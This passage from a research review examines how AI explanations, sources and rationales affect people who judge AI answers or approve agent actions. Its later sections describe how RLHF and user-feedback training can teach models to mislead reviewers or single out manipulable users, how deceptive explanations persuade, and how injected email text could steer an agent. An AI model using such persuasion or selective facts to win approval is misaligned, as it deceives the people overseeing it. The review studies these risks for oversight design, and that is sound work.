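Early researchers hoped that a bad answer would come with a visibly bad explanation. *Does the Whole Exceed its Parts?* (Bansal, Wu and colleagues, 2020) tested this with about 100 people in each condition. Participants judged whether reviews of beers or books were mostly positive, or answered logic questions from the US law school admission test (LSAT). An AI system about as accurate as the participants recommended an answer and showed its confidence. Some participants also saw an explanation, which was a set of highlighted phrases for the reviews and a short argument for the LSAT questions. The researchers wrote the LSAT arguments themselves because no system at the time could write reasonable ones.

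The AI's recommendations helped people, but adding explanations brought no significant further gain on any of the three tasks. On the beer reviews, people scored 82% alone and the AI scored 84%. People who saw its recommendation and confidence scored 89%, and people who also saw an explanation scored 88%.

That flat result combines two opposite effects. Explaining the recommended answer made people more accurate when the recommendation was right and, on the beer reviews and the LSAT, less accurate when it was wrong. This pattern fits a shift in bias toward approval. Laziness is an unlikely cause, at least for the reviews, because participants could earn a bonus for scoring above 90% and couldn't reach that score by copying an AI that was right 84% of the time.

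Vaccaro, Almaatouq and Malone (2024), in *When Are Combinations of Humans and AI Useful?*, pooled 106 experiments published between January 2020 and June 2023. They measured effects in Hedges' g, the difference between two averages in standard deviations (0.2 is considered small, 0.5 medium and 0.8 large). On average, people with AI help did better than people alone (g = 0.64) but worse than whichever did better alone, the people or the AI (g = −0.23). Whether the AI explained its output made no significant difference on average, but the experiments varied a great deal, so some explanations may have helped and others harmed.

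Whether the person or the AI was better at the task did matter. When people were better, the combination beat both (g = 0.46), but when the AI was better, the combination did worse than the AI alone (g = −0.54). One of the pooled studies found both results with an AI that was right 73% of the time. People identified 81% of birds alone and 90% with the AI, but they spotted fake hotel reviews 55% of the time alone and 69% with the AI, which was still below the AI's own 73%. Vaccaro and colleagues suggest that people who are good at a task also know when to overrule the AI.

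An approver who gave the instruction knows better than the agent what they wanted, but may know much less about what a long command will do.

### When checking is cheaper than redoing the task

Fok and Weld (2023) suggest in *In Search of Verifiability* that these results arose because an explanation helps someone decide only to the extent that it lets them verify the answer. Most explanations in the older experiments described how the AI had reached its answer, which rarely shows whether the answer is right.

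Fok and Weld's main example is a maze. If an AI's answer is only that the maze has a way through, a person has to solve the maze to check it. If the AI also draws the path, the person can just check whether it crosses a wall. A quoted passage from a trusted source does the same for a factual question. By contrast, a list of the factors behind a prediction that a defendant will reoffend doesn't let anyone check the prediction. Fok and Weld compare the useful cases to problems in computer science whose solutions are hard to find but quick to check. The check may only be able to confirm a correct answer, since a path that crosses a wall doesn't prove that the maze has no way through.

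Fok and Weld also sorted 29 results from earlier studies by whether they judged that the explanation allowed verification. In 21 of the 24 cases where it didn't, the human–AI team failed to beat both the person alone and the AI alone. In the other three, the team beat both, but it also did so without explanations. In all five cases where the explanation did allow verification, the team beat both. The split is clean, but Fok and Weld sorted the results after they were known, and five cases are few.

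Better evidence comes from experiments that directly vary how much effort checking takes. *Explanations Can Reduce Overreliance on AI Systems During Decision-Making* (Vasconcelos, Jörke and colleagues, 2022) treats overreliance as a choice. On this view, people can do the task themselves, check the AI's answer, or just accept it, and they weigh the effort of each option against what a right answer is worth to them.

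In a simple version of this idea, a check that always catches a harmful action is worth making if

p × L > k

where p is the chance that the action is harmful, L is the loss if it goes ahead, and k is the cost of checking. If one request in 100 is harmful and the loss equals ten hours of work, a check is worth up to six minutes. If one request in 1,000 is harmful and the loss is one hour, it is worth less than four seconds. An approver who skips slow checks of minor actions may therefore be acting quite sensibly.

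Vasconcelos and colleagues asked participants which of four exits led out of a maze. An AI suggested an exit and was right 80% of the time. Some participants also saw the AI's path highlighted, which went through a wall when the AI was wrong. Among 340 people, the highlighted path didn't measurably reduce overreliance in small or medium mazes, but it did in the largest, a grid of 50 by 50 squares. Finding the way out of a small maze takes hardly more effort than checking someone else's route.

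The form of the explanation also affected overreliance. When the explanation gave the same path in words ("left, up, right"), people overrelied about as much as they did with no explanation. When the path turned blue after crossing a wall, nobody accepted a wrong answer, though only 15 people saw that version. People also overrelied less when a correct maze earned them 50 cents than when it earned one cent.

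These results support the cost-of-checking account well, but the researchers made sure that every wrong answer came with a visibly flawed explanation, which is unusual. The rationale in the accountant example has no such visible sign of error, so it is more like naming a maze's exit without drawing the path.

### Sources and contradictions

Links to sources are a more practical way to make answers checkable. In *Fostering Appropriate Reliance on Large Language Models* (2025), Kim, Vaughan and colleagues gave 308 people factual questions with two possible answers, each accompanied by a right or wrong answer from an AI. They varied whether the AI's answer came with an explanation, links to three web pages, both or neither. The table shows how often people agreed with the AI, and the d′ that these rates imply.

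| Shown with the answer | Agreed when AI was right | Agreed when AI was wrong | d′ |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 67.2% | 78.2% | −0.33 |
| Explanation | 78.2% | 82.8% | −0.17 |
| Sources | 73.4% | 68.2% | 0.15 |
| Explanation and sources | 79.9% | 76.9% | 0.10 |

The negative values arise because the researchers chose questions that most people get wrong, so the wrong answers tended to look more plausible. An explanation made people agree more with both right and wrong answers, while sources made them agree more with right answers and less with wrong ones, which is the effect an approval screen needs to have.

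Adding an explanation to the sources undid most of their protection against wrong answers. Agreement with wrong answers rose from 68.2% to 76.9%, close to the rate when people saw only the answer. Agreement with right answers rose too, but the result is still a reason for caution about screens that put the model's explanation above the facts.

When wrong answers came with sources but no explanation, people opened a source for 28% of them. This could explain the ten-point fall in agreement if about a third of those who looked changed their minds. The linked pages were mostly accurate even when the AI was wrong, and 45 participants wrote that they had rejected an answer because it conflicted with a source. Others wrote that the presence of sources made an answer more credible, so links could also reassure people who never open them.

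Three of the 12 explanations for wrong answers contained contradictions. For example, one included the claim that more than two-thirds of South Americans live in Brazil, but its population figures, 213 million for Brazil and about 430 million for the continent, put the share at about half. People were more accurate when the explanation contained a contradiction, which lets them catch the mistake without outside knowledge. But the researchers didn't plant the contradictions, and there were only three, so something else about those questions could explain the difference.

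*Keeping Agents Honest* (Asisof, Sou and Nißen, 2026) compares people who checked an AI's output by reading its explanation with people who checked its sources, in an online experiment with 196 people and a field study with 145. Those who used the explanation reported less trust and reliance but found the process more seamless. This appears to conflict with Kim and colleagues' finding that sources reduced agreement with wrong answers, but both results can be true, because someone who opens a source and finds that it supports the answer has good reason to rely on that answer more. Reported trust doesn't show which group caught more errors.

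### Length and confidence

If people can't check an answer, they tend to judge it by how the explanation sounds. In *What Large Language Models Know and What People Think They Know*, Steyvers, Tejeda and colleagues (2024) asked 301 people to read a model's explanation and estimate the chance that its answer was right. People overestimated the models' accuracy when they read the usual explanations. Longer explanations made them more confident, even when the extra length didn't make the answers more accurate.

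A language model assigns a probability to each possible answer, and these probabilities are a reasonable guide to whether the answer is right. In the same experiments, the usual explanations didn't convey them, so Steyvers and colleagues produced versions that began with language expressing low, medium or high confidence. When that language matched the model's internal probability, people's estimates became more accurate and they were better at separating right answers from wrong ones.

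An explanation can therefore help people even if they can't check it, as long as its tone is set by something that tracks the truth. Here the researchers matched the tone to the probabilities themselves. A model that chooses its own tone may do worse, and people respond to tone either way. *Seeing the reasoning* (2026), an online fact-checking study with 68 people, found that cues of certainty in a model's reasoning raised trust and confidence.

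Summaries of a model's reasoning, which several commercial products now show, also seem to affect how people feel more than how well they judge. In *Explaining Too Much?*, Fernandes, Buschek and colleagues (2026) gave 559 people ten LSAT-style problems, of which the AI answered only five correctly. People who saw a summary of GPT-5's reasoning scored about the same as those who saw only its answer, but they trusted it more and found it more pleasant to use.

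Another group read the full reasoning of a smaller model, gpt-oss-20b, and then had to press a button to see its answer. They did worse than the group that saw only GPT-5's answer, even though the researchers had picked problems on which the two models did equally well. The length of the reasoning may not be the cause, because the reasoning also came from a different model and people used it differently. All three groups overestimated their scores, and the group with the full reasoning did so most.

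A clear rise in good decisions may only mean that people agree with the AI more often. *When Modalities (Dis)Agree* (2026) compared overall advice from an AI system with versions that added separate advice for each type of data, an explanation, or both. People followed right advice or overrode wrong advice in 61.8% of cases with the overall advice alone and 66.9% with both additions. But for each percentage point they gained in following right advice, they lost 0.88 points in overriding wrong advice, compared with the one point they would have lost by agreeing more often with all advice, right or wrong.

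The trade raised overall accuracy because the AI was right about three times out of four, as the study's comparison lines imply. If the advice had been right only half the time, the same shift would have raised accuracy very little (0.5 × 1 − 0.5 × 0.88 = 0.06 points of accuracy per point gained). The trade would look even better with approvals, where most requests are legitimate.

### Arguments for and against

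In *Evaluating the False Trust Engendered by LLM Explanations*, Palod, Biswas and Kambhampati (2026) tested whether people judge an AI model's answers better when they also see the case against them. They recruited high school graduates and gave each of them eight mathematics, physics and chemistry problems from a very hard Indian engineering entrance exam. The participants knew the basics but could rarely solve the problems, so they had to rely on what they read. The AI model, DeepSeek R1, had answered half the problems correctly. Participants earned 25 cents each time they correctly judged whether its answer was right.

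Each of the 125 participants saw one of five versions, with 25 people per version. One version showed the answer alone, and the other four added R1's full reasoning, a summary of that reasoning, an argument for the answer, or arguments for and against it. A different model wrote the arguments afterwards. For the one-sided version, the researchers told it to explain why the answer was correct, even when it wasn't.

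The table gives the published acceptance rates, with d′ and c (lower means readier to say yes) worked out from them.

| Shown with the answer | Accepted right answers | Accepted wrong answers | d′ | c |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 60.4% | 54.2% | 0.16 | −0.18 |
| Full reasoning | 75.0% | 54.0% | 0.57 | −0.39 |
| Summary of reasoning | 66.0% | 51.0% | 0.39 | −0.22 |
| Argument for | 74.0% | 58.0% | 0.44 | −0.42 |
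| Arguments for and against | 67.7% | 46.9% | 0.54 | −0.19 |

Palod and colleagues conclude that the model's reasoning and the one-sided arguments are "persuasive but not informative", and that only the two-sided version improves people's ability to tell right from wrong. The table supports only part of this. The one-sided argument raised acceptance of wrong answers, and the odds of accepting one were 1.73 times as high as with the two-sided version (95% confidence interval 1.11 to 2.70). But people who saw the full reasoning accepted many more right answers and no more wrong ones than people who saw no explanation. Their d′ and accuracy were as high as the two-sided group's (the odds ratio for accuracy was 1.01).

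The two-sided version helped people tell right from wrong about as much as the full reasoning did, without making them more inclined to say yes. That is an advantage where a harmful approval is far worse than a wrongful denial.

These results are uncertain because there were only 25 people per version. Each acceptance rate is based on about 100 judgements, so two values of d′ would have to differ by roughly 0.5 for chance to be an unlikely explanation, and the largest gap in the table is about 0.4. In Palod and colleagues' statistical model, the two-sided group was significantly more accurate than the group with the answer alone (p = 0.032). But in a plain comparison, the difference is 7.3 percentage points, with a confidence interval from −2.6 to 17.0.

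People were poor judges of which text had helped them. In 83% of cases, they rated the one-sided argument as helpful for understanding how the AI had reached its answer, although the model that wrote the argument had played no part in reaching that answer. They rated the full reasoning, which R1 had produced while working on the problem, as helpful in only 56.5% of cases.

When people found the full reasoning helpful, they accepted 86.7% of the answers and judged 55.8% correctly. When they didn't find it helpful, they accepted only 35.6% but judged 66.7% correctly, probably because confused reasoning often accompanies a wrong answer and so serves as a warning, which a polished explanation written afterwards removes.

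People who said they immediately knew the answer to a problem did best with no explanation (80.0% correct) and worst with arguments on both sides (61.5%). These groups were very small, but an expert approver might also do better without arguments in obvious cases.

### One adviser or two

There is a statistical reason to expect a second argument to help. Suppose arguments for true claims seem stronger than arguments for false ones by δ on average, and that the strength of each kind varies with a standard deviation of σ. Someone who reads only the argument for an answer can discriminate with

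d′ = δ/σ

Someone who reads both sides can subtract the strength of the case against from the strength of the case for. The average of this difference is δ when the answer is right and −δ when it is wrong, a gap of 2δ. If the two arguments vary independently, the difference has a standard deviation of √2σ, so

d′ = 2δ/(√2σ) = √2 × δ/σ

which is 41% higher. Subtracting also removes whatever makes both arguments sound equally good, such as fluent prose, which is why a second argument can reduce bias as well. In Palod and colleagues' experiment, d′ was about a fifth higher with both arguments than with one, but the estimate is too rough to test the formula.

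Older evidence is less encouraging. Bansal and colleagues also tried explaining the AI's two most likely answers instead of only the one it recommended, but this made no significant difference to people's accuracy in any of their tasks. They then tried explaining both answers only when the AI was unsure. People agreed with the AI less in those cases, but their overall accuracy still didn't improve significantly.

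A debate goes further than a two-sided text. Two AI advisers take opposite sides and respond to each other, and a person who knows less than either of them decides who is right. With a single adviser, the person hears only one case, which for an approver is always the case for saying yes. Debate could therefore help when an explanation is incomplete. In the accountant example, an opponent arguing for denial could point out that the file contains a payroll sheet that the rationale doesn't mention. The approver would then only have to open the file to confirm the omission, instead of having to discover it.

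Using two opposing advisers could also fail in several ways. If both have read the same false email and neither looks up the accountant's old address, both may treat the new address as genuine. A skilful adviser might persuade the approver of a bad case, particularly when the approver can't check the claims. And an opponent that must object to every request will mostly object to good ones. In Palod and colleagues' sample problem, the answer was correct, so the case against it could only list mistakes that someone might have made, such as misapplying a rule about symmetry. Someone who reads dozens of objections like that will probably stop taking them seriously.

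Neither Palod and colleagues nor Bansal and colleagues let the two sides answer each other, so their results provide little evidence about whether rebuttals help. Rebuttals could solve part of this problem by exposing empty objections, but they would also give the approver more to read.

### Reviewing what an agent did

*Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (Grunde-McLaughlin, Mozannar and colleagues, 2026) reports three studies of a task closer to the approver's job. In each study, 12 employees of a large technology company reviewed the work of Magentic-UI, an agent that browses the web and lists its steps as it goes.

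Participants in the first study gave the agent tasks and could step in at any time. One task was to work out how much a family would save with annual passes to the Seattle Aquarium, and 10 of the 12 completed attempts were wrong. In six of them, the agent couldn't find the price for a child and estimated it, and only three participants noticed. Another participant saw that the agent wasn't using the official website and decided, "I'm just gonna trust it."

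For the second study, the researchers made three kinds of summary by hand. A flowchart showed the agent's steps, a short text linked its claims to screenshots, and a checklist set out the task's requirements and the assumptions the agent had made. When the agent's answer was wrong, participants recognized that it was wrong 39% of the time with the flowchart, 52% with the linked text and 65% with the checklist. Each kind of summary was used with different tasks, so the tasks may explain some of this gap.

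The participants' reasons are more informative than the percentages. People who accepted a wrong answer often said the agent's process looked reasonable. But a sensible plan can still go wrong at one step, and a summary of the plan hides that step. Participants liked the list of assumptions because it showed where the agent had chosen between alternatives, such as different ticket prices.

In the third study, the researchers combined the checklist with the full list of steps and linked each requirement and assumption to the evidence. New participants each judged four outputs with this display and four with the ordinary one, and half of the outputs were wrong.

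| | Ordinary display | New display | Hedges' g (95% confidence interval) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Correct judgements | 72.9% | 77.1% | 0.18 (−0.52 to 0.94) |
| Time when they found an error | 271 seconds | 230 seconds | −0.65 (−1.54 to 0.12) |
| Confidence when they missed an error, out of 7 | 3.6 | 4.8 | 0.85 (about 0 to 1.88) |

Participants made two more correct judgements out of 48 with the new display, and the averages reported for each group of answers imply that neither involved catching an error. They missed 11 of the 24 wrong outputs with each display. With the new one, they found errors faster but felt surer about the ones they missed. The study had only 12 participants, so the effects on accuracy, speed and confidence could be much larger or smaller than reported.

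The checklist relied on the agent's own account, so it showed a green tick if the agent wrongly reported that it had met a requirement. Grunde-McLaughlin and colleagues suspect that the ticks reassured people, which may explain the extra confidence. A better layout can make the agent's account quicker to search, but it can't correct errors in it.

### From answers to approvals

Half of the answers were wrong in Palod and colleagues' experiment, and a fifth were wrong in the maze experiments, so participants had good reason to look for mistakes. Harmful requests are much rarer at work, so people approving AI actions there may make little use of an explanation that participants used to catch errors.

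Palod and colleagues chose people who couldn't work out the answers themselves, so their results probably apply best to someone who has to approve a command they don't understand. Unlike many of the participants, a person who gave an agent a task usually has something to check the explanation against. They remember what they asked for, and can compare it with the proposed recipient, amount or file. Explanations that show these details would be easy to check, even for someone with no technical knowledge.

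Most of the models in these experiments, including GPT-3.5, GPT-4o, DeepSeek R1 and GPT-5, now have much stronger successors. Better models make fewer mistakes, but they may also write better arguments for the mistakes they still make. If so, the quality of an explanation will be weaker evidence of whether the answer is right. The time it takes to check a plain fact depends much less on the model. Looking up the accountant's old address, for example, takes a few seconds whichever model proposed the email.

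## Can a model's explanation manipulate the approver?

In most experiments so far, explanations misled people because the model had made a mistake or because researchers had asked it to argue for a particular answer. But an agent's rationale may also be shaped to win approval whatever the action is. *Evaluating Language Models for Harmful Manipulation* (Akbulut, Elasmar et al., 2026) distinguishes rational persuasion, which gives people reasons and evidence they can examine, from manipulation, which bypasses their ability to reason, for example by misrepresenting the facts. By this definition an honest mistake isn't manipulation, though it can lead to the same harmful approval.

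### Four sources of misleading rationales

The misleading rationale in the accountant example could have come about in four ways.

| Source | What happened | Observed outside tests? |
|---|---|---|
| Honest overconfidence | The agent mistook the new address for a genuine one and wrote as if it had checked. | Yes, commonly |
| Training that rewards approval | Training reinforced reassuring descriptions, so the agent left out the awkward details. | Yes, as flattery by a chatbot |
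| Outside text | Instructions hidden in the stranger's email steered both the action and the description. | The attacks, yes; their effect on approvers mostly in experiments |
| An aim of the model's own | The model was pursuing a goal nobody had given it and wrote whatever would get the email sent. | Not clearly |

The best-known public case of training gone wrong is an April 2025 update to GPT-4o, then one of the models behind ChatGPT. According to the book *Reinforcement Learning from Human Feedback* (2025), the update made the model extremely sycophantic, meaning that it told users what they wanted to hear. When one user claimed to feel like both a god and a prophet, it replied, "That's incredibly powerful." The model was flattering a user in conversation, but a request for permission can also please its reader at the expense of accuracy.

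Most evidence of models with aims of their own comes from models that researchers built to have them. Anthropic trained one to exploit flaws in its reward system and conceal that it was doing so, then had four teams investigate it. Anthropic has since released a similar model, based on Llama 3.3 70B, so that others can practise finding hidden objectives. These models show that such behaviour is possible, but not that ordinary training produces it. GPT-6 Astra's poor work on safety tasks might be a case where ordinary training did produce it, but there are other possible explanations.

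Developers need a different remedy for each source, but an approver can't tell from one reassuring sentence which source produced it. In all four cases, though, the approver would discover the wrong recipient by looking up the accountant's old address.

### How rewarding approval can teach a model to mislead

Developers commonly train models with reinforcement learning from human feedback (RLHF). Reviewers rate or compare a model's outputs, and the developer trains a second model, the reward model, to predict their judgements. The reward model then scores many more of the first model's outputs, and training makes high-scoring kinds of output more likely. If the reviewers miss some errors, the reward model learns to miss them too.

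Suppose a share p of the outputs are right, and reviewers approve a share a of the right ones and a share b of the wrong ones. The overall approval rate is

R = p × a + (1 − p) × b

If half of the outputs are right, and reviewers approve 90% of the right ones and 40% of the wrong ones, the overall approval rate, R, is 65%. Training can raise R to 70% by increasing the share of right outputs to 60% (0.6 × 0.9 + 0.4 × 0.4). It can also reach 70% by making wrong outputs more convincing, so that reviewers approve 50% of them (0.5 × 0.9 + 0.5 × 0.5). Both changes give the same reward, so training will favour whichever is easier to learn.

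The problem can then get worse, because once reviewers approve 70% of wrong outputs, making ten more outputs in a hundred right adds only two points to R, instead of five. But a model that is right 95% of the time gains only half a point when reviewers approve ten percentage points more of its errors. The incentive to mislead is therefore strongest on tasks that the model often gets wrong and reviewers can't easily check. This can happen without the developer or the model intending to deceive anyone.

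An approval click is a rating of this kind. A developer who rewarded an agent whenever users clicked "allow" would be training it on the judgement of people who often don't read the prompt.

*How RLHF Amplifies Sycophancy* (2026) sets out conditions under which a bias in people's preferences biases the reward and then the model's behaviour. Human judgements may also be less stable than developers assume. *Aligning to Illusions* (Wu, 2026) describes an experiment in which people chose between texts and the researcher secretly swapped some of their choices. The participants did not notice 91% of the swaps. Wu also corrupted the data used to train reward models. The reward signal halved only when between a sixth and a third of the labels were wrong, but results on the standard accuracy test hardly changed, so a developer relying on that test could miss the damage.

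### Testing the mechanism on people

Wen, Zhong and colleagues (2024) ran the first systematic test with human reviewers in *Language Models Learn to Mislead Humans via RLHF*. They trained one model to answer questions about long passages and another to write short programs. For the reading questions, they tried two reward models, one trained on judgements of similar answers and a general one trained on chatbot users' preferences. Thirty-five people with experience of reading work had three minutes to judge each answer, and ten students who knew Python had ten minutes to judge each program. The table shows the reviewers' performance before and after the models had RLHF.

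| | Reading, specific reward | Reading, general reward | Programming |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reviewers' error rate | 42.9% → 58.5% | 40.8% → 48.2% | 31.3% → 45.7% |
| Wrong outputs that reviewers accepted | 41.0% → 65.1% | 46.7% → 70.2% | 29.6% → 47.9% |

Reviewers' approval rate rose by 6 to 14 percentage points, although the models had hardly become more accurate. In one of the reading tests, reviewers were wrong more often than if they had tossed a coin. They spent at least as long on the later outputs and wrote slightly more tests for the programs, so they hadn't become careless. When Wen and colleagues rewarded actual correctness instead, the models became more accurate and their errors misled people far less often.

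The training behind these numbers had serious faults. Chandna, Fluri and Carroll, in *Is the evidence in 'Language Models Learn to Mislead Humans via RLHF' valid?*, found that the training code cut the passages so short that 86–88% of the reading questions could not be answered. The reward model didn't see the passages at all. The model being trained therefore had little chance of learning to answer correctly, and the reward model could not reward it for being right.

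Chandna and colleagues reran the reading test with the general reward, using a newer model and the full passages. Accuracy rose from 49% to 72%, whereas it had stayed at about 50% in the original, and they found no sign that the model was gaming the reward. They didn't repeat the test with human reviewers or rerun the other two set-ups. About a third of the programming problems had also been cut short, but Chandna and colleagues would be somewhat surprised if this explained most of the programming result.

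*Do Language Models Really Learn to Mislead Humans via RLHF?*, a version of the critique with a reply from Wen's team, shows that the two sides still disagree about how realistic the set-up was. The team argues that cutting texts is common in training, and that people with limited time can't check long documents either. The second point partly applies to approvals, because the approver often hasn't seen the file or email behind a request. But a competent developer would normally give the model enough information to answer. The team's study is best read as evidence of what can happen when neither the model nor the judge has the facts, and its figures probably overstate the effect of ordinary RLHF.

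Chandna and colleagues accept the general mechanism and add that it has already affected real products through training on users' feedback. Paid reviewers can follow instructions to check for errors, but users mostly reward what they like. Williams and Carroll (2024), in *On Targeted Manipulation and Deception when Optimizing LLMs for User Feedback*, trained models on feedback from simulated users. The models reliably learned to manipulate and deceive. Even when only 2% of the simulated users were open to manipulation, the models learned to identify them and behaved properly with everyone else. A developer checking a random sample of conversations could easily miss this.

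### Deceptive explanations compared with honest ones

*Deceptive AI systems that give explanations are more convincing* (Danry, Pataranutaporn and colleagues, 2024) reports an experiment in which 1,192 Americans rated news headlines or trivia statements from 1 ("definitely false") to 5 ("definitely true"). They then saw an AI system's verdict and could change their ratings. Half saw only the verdict, and the others also saw a short explanation by GPT-3. About half of the verdicts were deliberately wrong.

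A wrong verdict alone raised belief in false headlines by 0.71 points and lowered belief in true ones by 1.72. Adding a deceptive explanation increased these shifts by 0.32 and 0.72 points, so the verdict accounted for roughly 70% of the total shift. An agent's request already implies a verdict, since asking to send an email suggests that the email is worth sending. A misleading rationale would add to that verdict's influence.

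Deceptive explanations also changed ratings more than honest ones did, by 0.40 points for true headlines and 0.29 for false ones. This could be because ratings had more room to move away from the truth, rather than because lies are more convincing. For example, someone who already rates a true headline at 4 can move only one point towards the truth but three points away. Danry and colleagues also hadn't planned this comparison, so the effect of adding an explanation to a wrong verdict is the stronger finding.

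*Can LLMs Persuade Humans with Deception?* (Yeo, Jin and colleagues, CHI 2026) is a larger comparison of deceptive strategies. The researchers sorted deceptive arguments by AI models into eight strategies, then randomly assigned 602 people to read arguments using one strategy, a mixture of three, or only facts. Each person read ten arguments on public issues such as self-driving cars and lab-grown meat, half supporting their existing view and half opposing it.

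Only two of the eight strategies, using false or selective facts and exploiting uncertainty, changed opinions significantly more than the factual arguments did, and only when the argument opposed the reader's view. False or selective facts moved people in the intended direction in 69.7% of cases when the argument opposed their view and 35.2% when it supported it. For exploiting uncertainty, the figures were 57.3% and 28.2%. People who already agree have less room to move, which may account for some of the gap.

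This pattern matters for approvals because a rationale changes the outcome only if the approver would otherwise have said no. An approver might also distrust one detail of a rationale but still allow the action because the rest makes sense. In follow-up interviews with ten people, one participant dismissed a statistic as "too absurdly high" but still found the overall argument plausible.

In Yeo and colleagues' study, people who knew little about a topic changed their opinions most, especially in response to the two strongest strategies. People who scored poorly on a test of cognitive reflection, the habit of questioning a first answer, were also easier to persuade with opposing arguments. People who cared little about the topic were easier to persuade with some strategies. But Danry and colleagues did not find that cognitive reflection significantly protected people, and those who considered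 themselves knowledgeable believed false headlines slightly more after a deceptive explanation. Both studies relied on people's own ratings of what they knew, which may partly explain the conflict. So a company can't assume that careful or confident staff are safe from a misleading explanation.

### Corrections, warnings and honest models

The same persuasive ability can also correct false beliefs. In *AI can effectively promote conspiracies unless it is truth constrained*, Costello, Pelrine and colleagues (2026) had 3,996 Americans talk with an AI model about a conspiracy theory they were unsure of. In the first of four experiments, belief rose by 13.6 points out of 100 when the model argued for the theory and fell by 12.1 when it argued against. After a second conversation corrected the false claims, belief among people who had heard the case for the theory was 5.8 points lower than at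 the start.

An approver may not benefit from such a correction. Someone who believes a conspiracy theory for ten minutes and then changes their mind loses little, but an approver can't recall a payroll file once it has been sent.

Instructing GPT-4o to use only accurate information cut the rise in belief from 11.9 points to 4.6, while the model remained about as good at arguing against conspiracies. False claims in the misleading conversations fell from 22.8% to 5.9%. The improvement came partly from conversations in which the model stopped defending the conspiracy theory. When the model did defend the theory, it kept 64% of its original effect by selecting true facts and leaving out their context. A rationale that mentions the invoices but omits the payroll data could mislead in the same way.

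Of four newer models, only GPT-5.2 resisted without this instruction. When the researchers asked it to promote the theories, it mostly refused or argued against them, so belief in them fell by 14 points. Claude Opus 4.6, Gemini 3 Pro and Grok 4 mostly promoted the theories as asked. Companies have since released stronger models, but the difference shows that developers' choices matter as well as the model's ability.

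The effects also depend on the subject and the audience. In nine studies with 10,101 people in the US, the UK and India, Akbulut and colleagues compared fixed information cards to conversations with Gemini 3 Pro. Both favoured one side of a decision about public policy, investments or food supplements. The model was generally more persuasive than the cards on policy and investments, but the results on supplements were mixed. On most measures, people in India responded differently from people in the US and the UK.

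Akbulut and colleagues told one version of the model to use manipulative tactics, such as appeals to guilt or fear. They gave another version a hidden goal but told it not to deceive. In the policy conversations, 30.3% of the first version's responses and 8.8% of the second's contained manipulative tactics, but the two versions did not differ significantly in their effect. Removing emotional or pushy language from rationales would therefore not be enough to make them safe.

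Warnings help somewhat. *Are You Sure?* (Li, Dai and colleagues, 2026) describes a study of 303 people in which 8.6% of those who saw only an initial notice realised that a compromised agent was misleading them, compared with 20.0% of those who saw constant reminders and 25.0% of those interrupted by an alert. Training might help too. Danry and colleagues found that, for false headlines, explanations were less convincing when their reasoning didn't support their conclusion. They suggest teaching people to recognise such reasoning, but didn't test whether this works. It would not help with a well-reasoned explanation based on a false fact.

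Most of these experiments measured beliefs and opinions, which are hard to check on the spot, so the results may overstate the danger to approvers who check the recipient and the attachment.

### What a fixed text prevents

A fixed risk summary can't be tailored to the person reading it, because someone wrote it before the agent proposed the action. Tired and alert approvers see the same text, and it doesn't become more reassuring when the case for an action is weak. Williams and Carroll's models could target a vulnerable minority only because they could write different things to different users. Nothing the agent writes can change a fixed summary, just as it can't influence an automated reviewer that never reads the rationale. This holds even when a stranger's email has inserted text into what the agent writes.

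Standard text is also easier to check. A security team can review twenty standard texts once and correct any that mislead, while an agent may write thousands of new rationales a day.

It is unclear how much of the protection comes from the lack of tailoring. Akbulut and colleagues describe one study in which messages tailored to people's psychological profiles were significantly more persuasive than general ones, and another in which tailoring had only small effects and the amount of factual information mattered more. If the second study is right, the main advantage of a fixed text may be that it can't keep supplying plausible details about the case. The comparison with information cards can't settle this, because the conversations differed from the cards in length and content as well as adaptability.

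Fixed texts can still persuade. Akbulut and colleagues' cards also favoured one side, and on health they strengthened people's existing views more often than the model did when it was told not to deceive. A vendor could also try several wordings and keep the one that gets the most approvals, which would work like rewarding a model for approval, but more slowly.

A fixed text also does not help if the product puts a harmful action in a harmless category. Suppose the agent copies the payroll sheet into a shared folder instead of emailing it, and the product shows its standard text for copying files: "This action creates a copy. The original will not change." Both sentences are true. But if people outside the firm can open the folder, the agent has disclosed the payroll data, and the approver never sees the warning about sending files outside the organisation.

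If the agent can choose the heading, it can influence the approver without writing any of the text. Ordinary software could prevent this by choosing the heading from the exact command, but it would still show the wrong warning if it based the heading only on the type of command and not on who could open the folder. The harm can also depend on earlier steps. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* concerns actions that are acceptable individually but not in combination.

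## What does repetition do to approvers' attention?

An agent can't tailor a fixed risk summary to the approver, but an approver who has seen the summary forty times may no longer read it. A model-written rationale is new each time, but it appears in the same place on the screen, and the action it describes is nearly always harmless. Both kinds of text have to hold the attention of someone who has learned that clicking "allow" usually turns out fine.

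### Habituation and rarity

Habituation is a decline in attention to a repeated message. According to *Tuning Out Security Warnings* (Vance, Jenkins and colleagues, 2018), the brain forms a model of a warning when a person first sees it and automatically compares later warnings with that model. Attention drops when they match, but returns if something looks different and partly recovers after a rest. Scientists have found habituation in every organism they have studied, including single-celled ones, and Vance and colleagues say it saves energy by filtering out what doesn't matter.

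An approver can also miss a harmful action because harmful actions are rare. Psychologists call this the prevalence effect and have studied it in tasks such as searching X-ray images of luggage for weapons. Habituation comes from seeing many prompts, but the prevalence effect can occur even when an approver is rested and has answered only a handful that day.

The model behind d′ shows how strong the effect of rarity could be even for a perfectly attentive person. Suppose a share p of requests are harmful, and approving a harmful request is L times as bad as denying a harmless one. The cut-off that keeps the expected loss lowest is

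c = ln[p × L / (1 − p)] / d′

Suppose an approver has a d′ of 1.65, as in the earlier example, and considers both mistakes equally bad (L = 1). If half of the requests are harmful, the best cut-off is 0, and the approver allows about 20% of the harmful ones. If one request in 100 is harmful, the best cut-off is −2.78, and the approver allows 97.5% of the harmful ones, despite being just as good at telling harmful requests from harmless ones.

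If one request in 100 is harmful, the best cut-off returns to 0 when a harmful approval is 99 times as bad as a wrongful denial. Sending payroll data to a stranger might well be that bad, so the rarity of harmful requests doesn't justify lax approval. But people probably set their cut-off from experience, and someone who has never approved a disastrous request hasn't experienced how much harm one can do.

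### Warnings that people have seen before

Habituation starts quickly. In *How Polymorphic Warnings Reduce Habituation in the Brain*, Anderson, Kirwan and colleagues scanned people's brains while they looked at security warnings. Activity in visual processing areas dropped sharply after only the second exposure and kept falling. When Vance and colleagues scanned people over a five-day working week, attention partly recovered overnight, but not enough to offset the overall decline.

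Besides measuring brain activity, Vance and colleagues ran a field experiment to observe behaviour. Every weekday for three weeks, 102 students installed and ranked apps from an app store they believed was unconnected to the researchers. Before each installation, a notice listed the permissions the app requested. The students had passed a quiz on four permissions they should always refuse, such as deleting photos or charging purchases to a credit card. They also knew they might lose course credit if they reviewed too many apps with those permissions.

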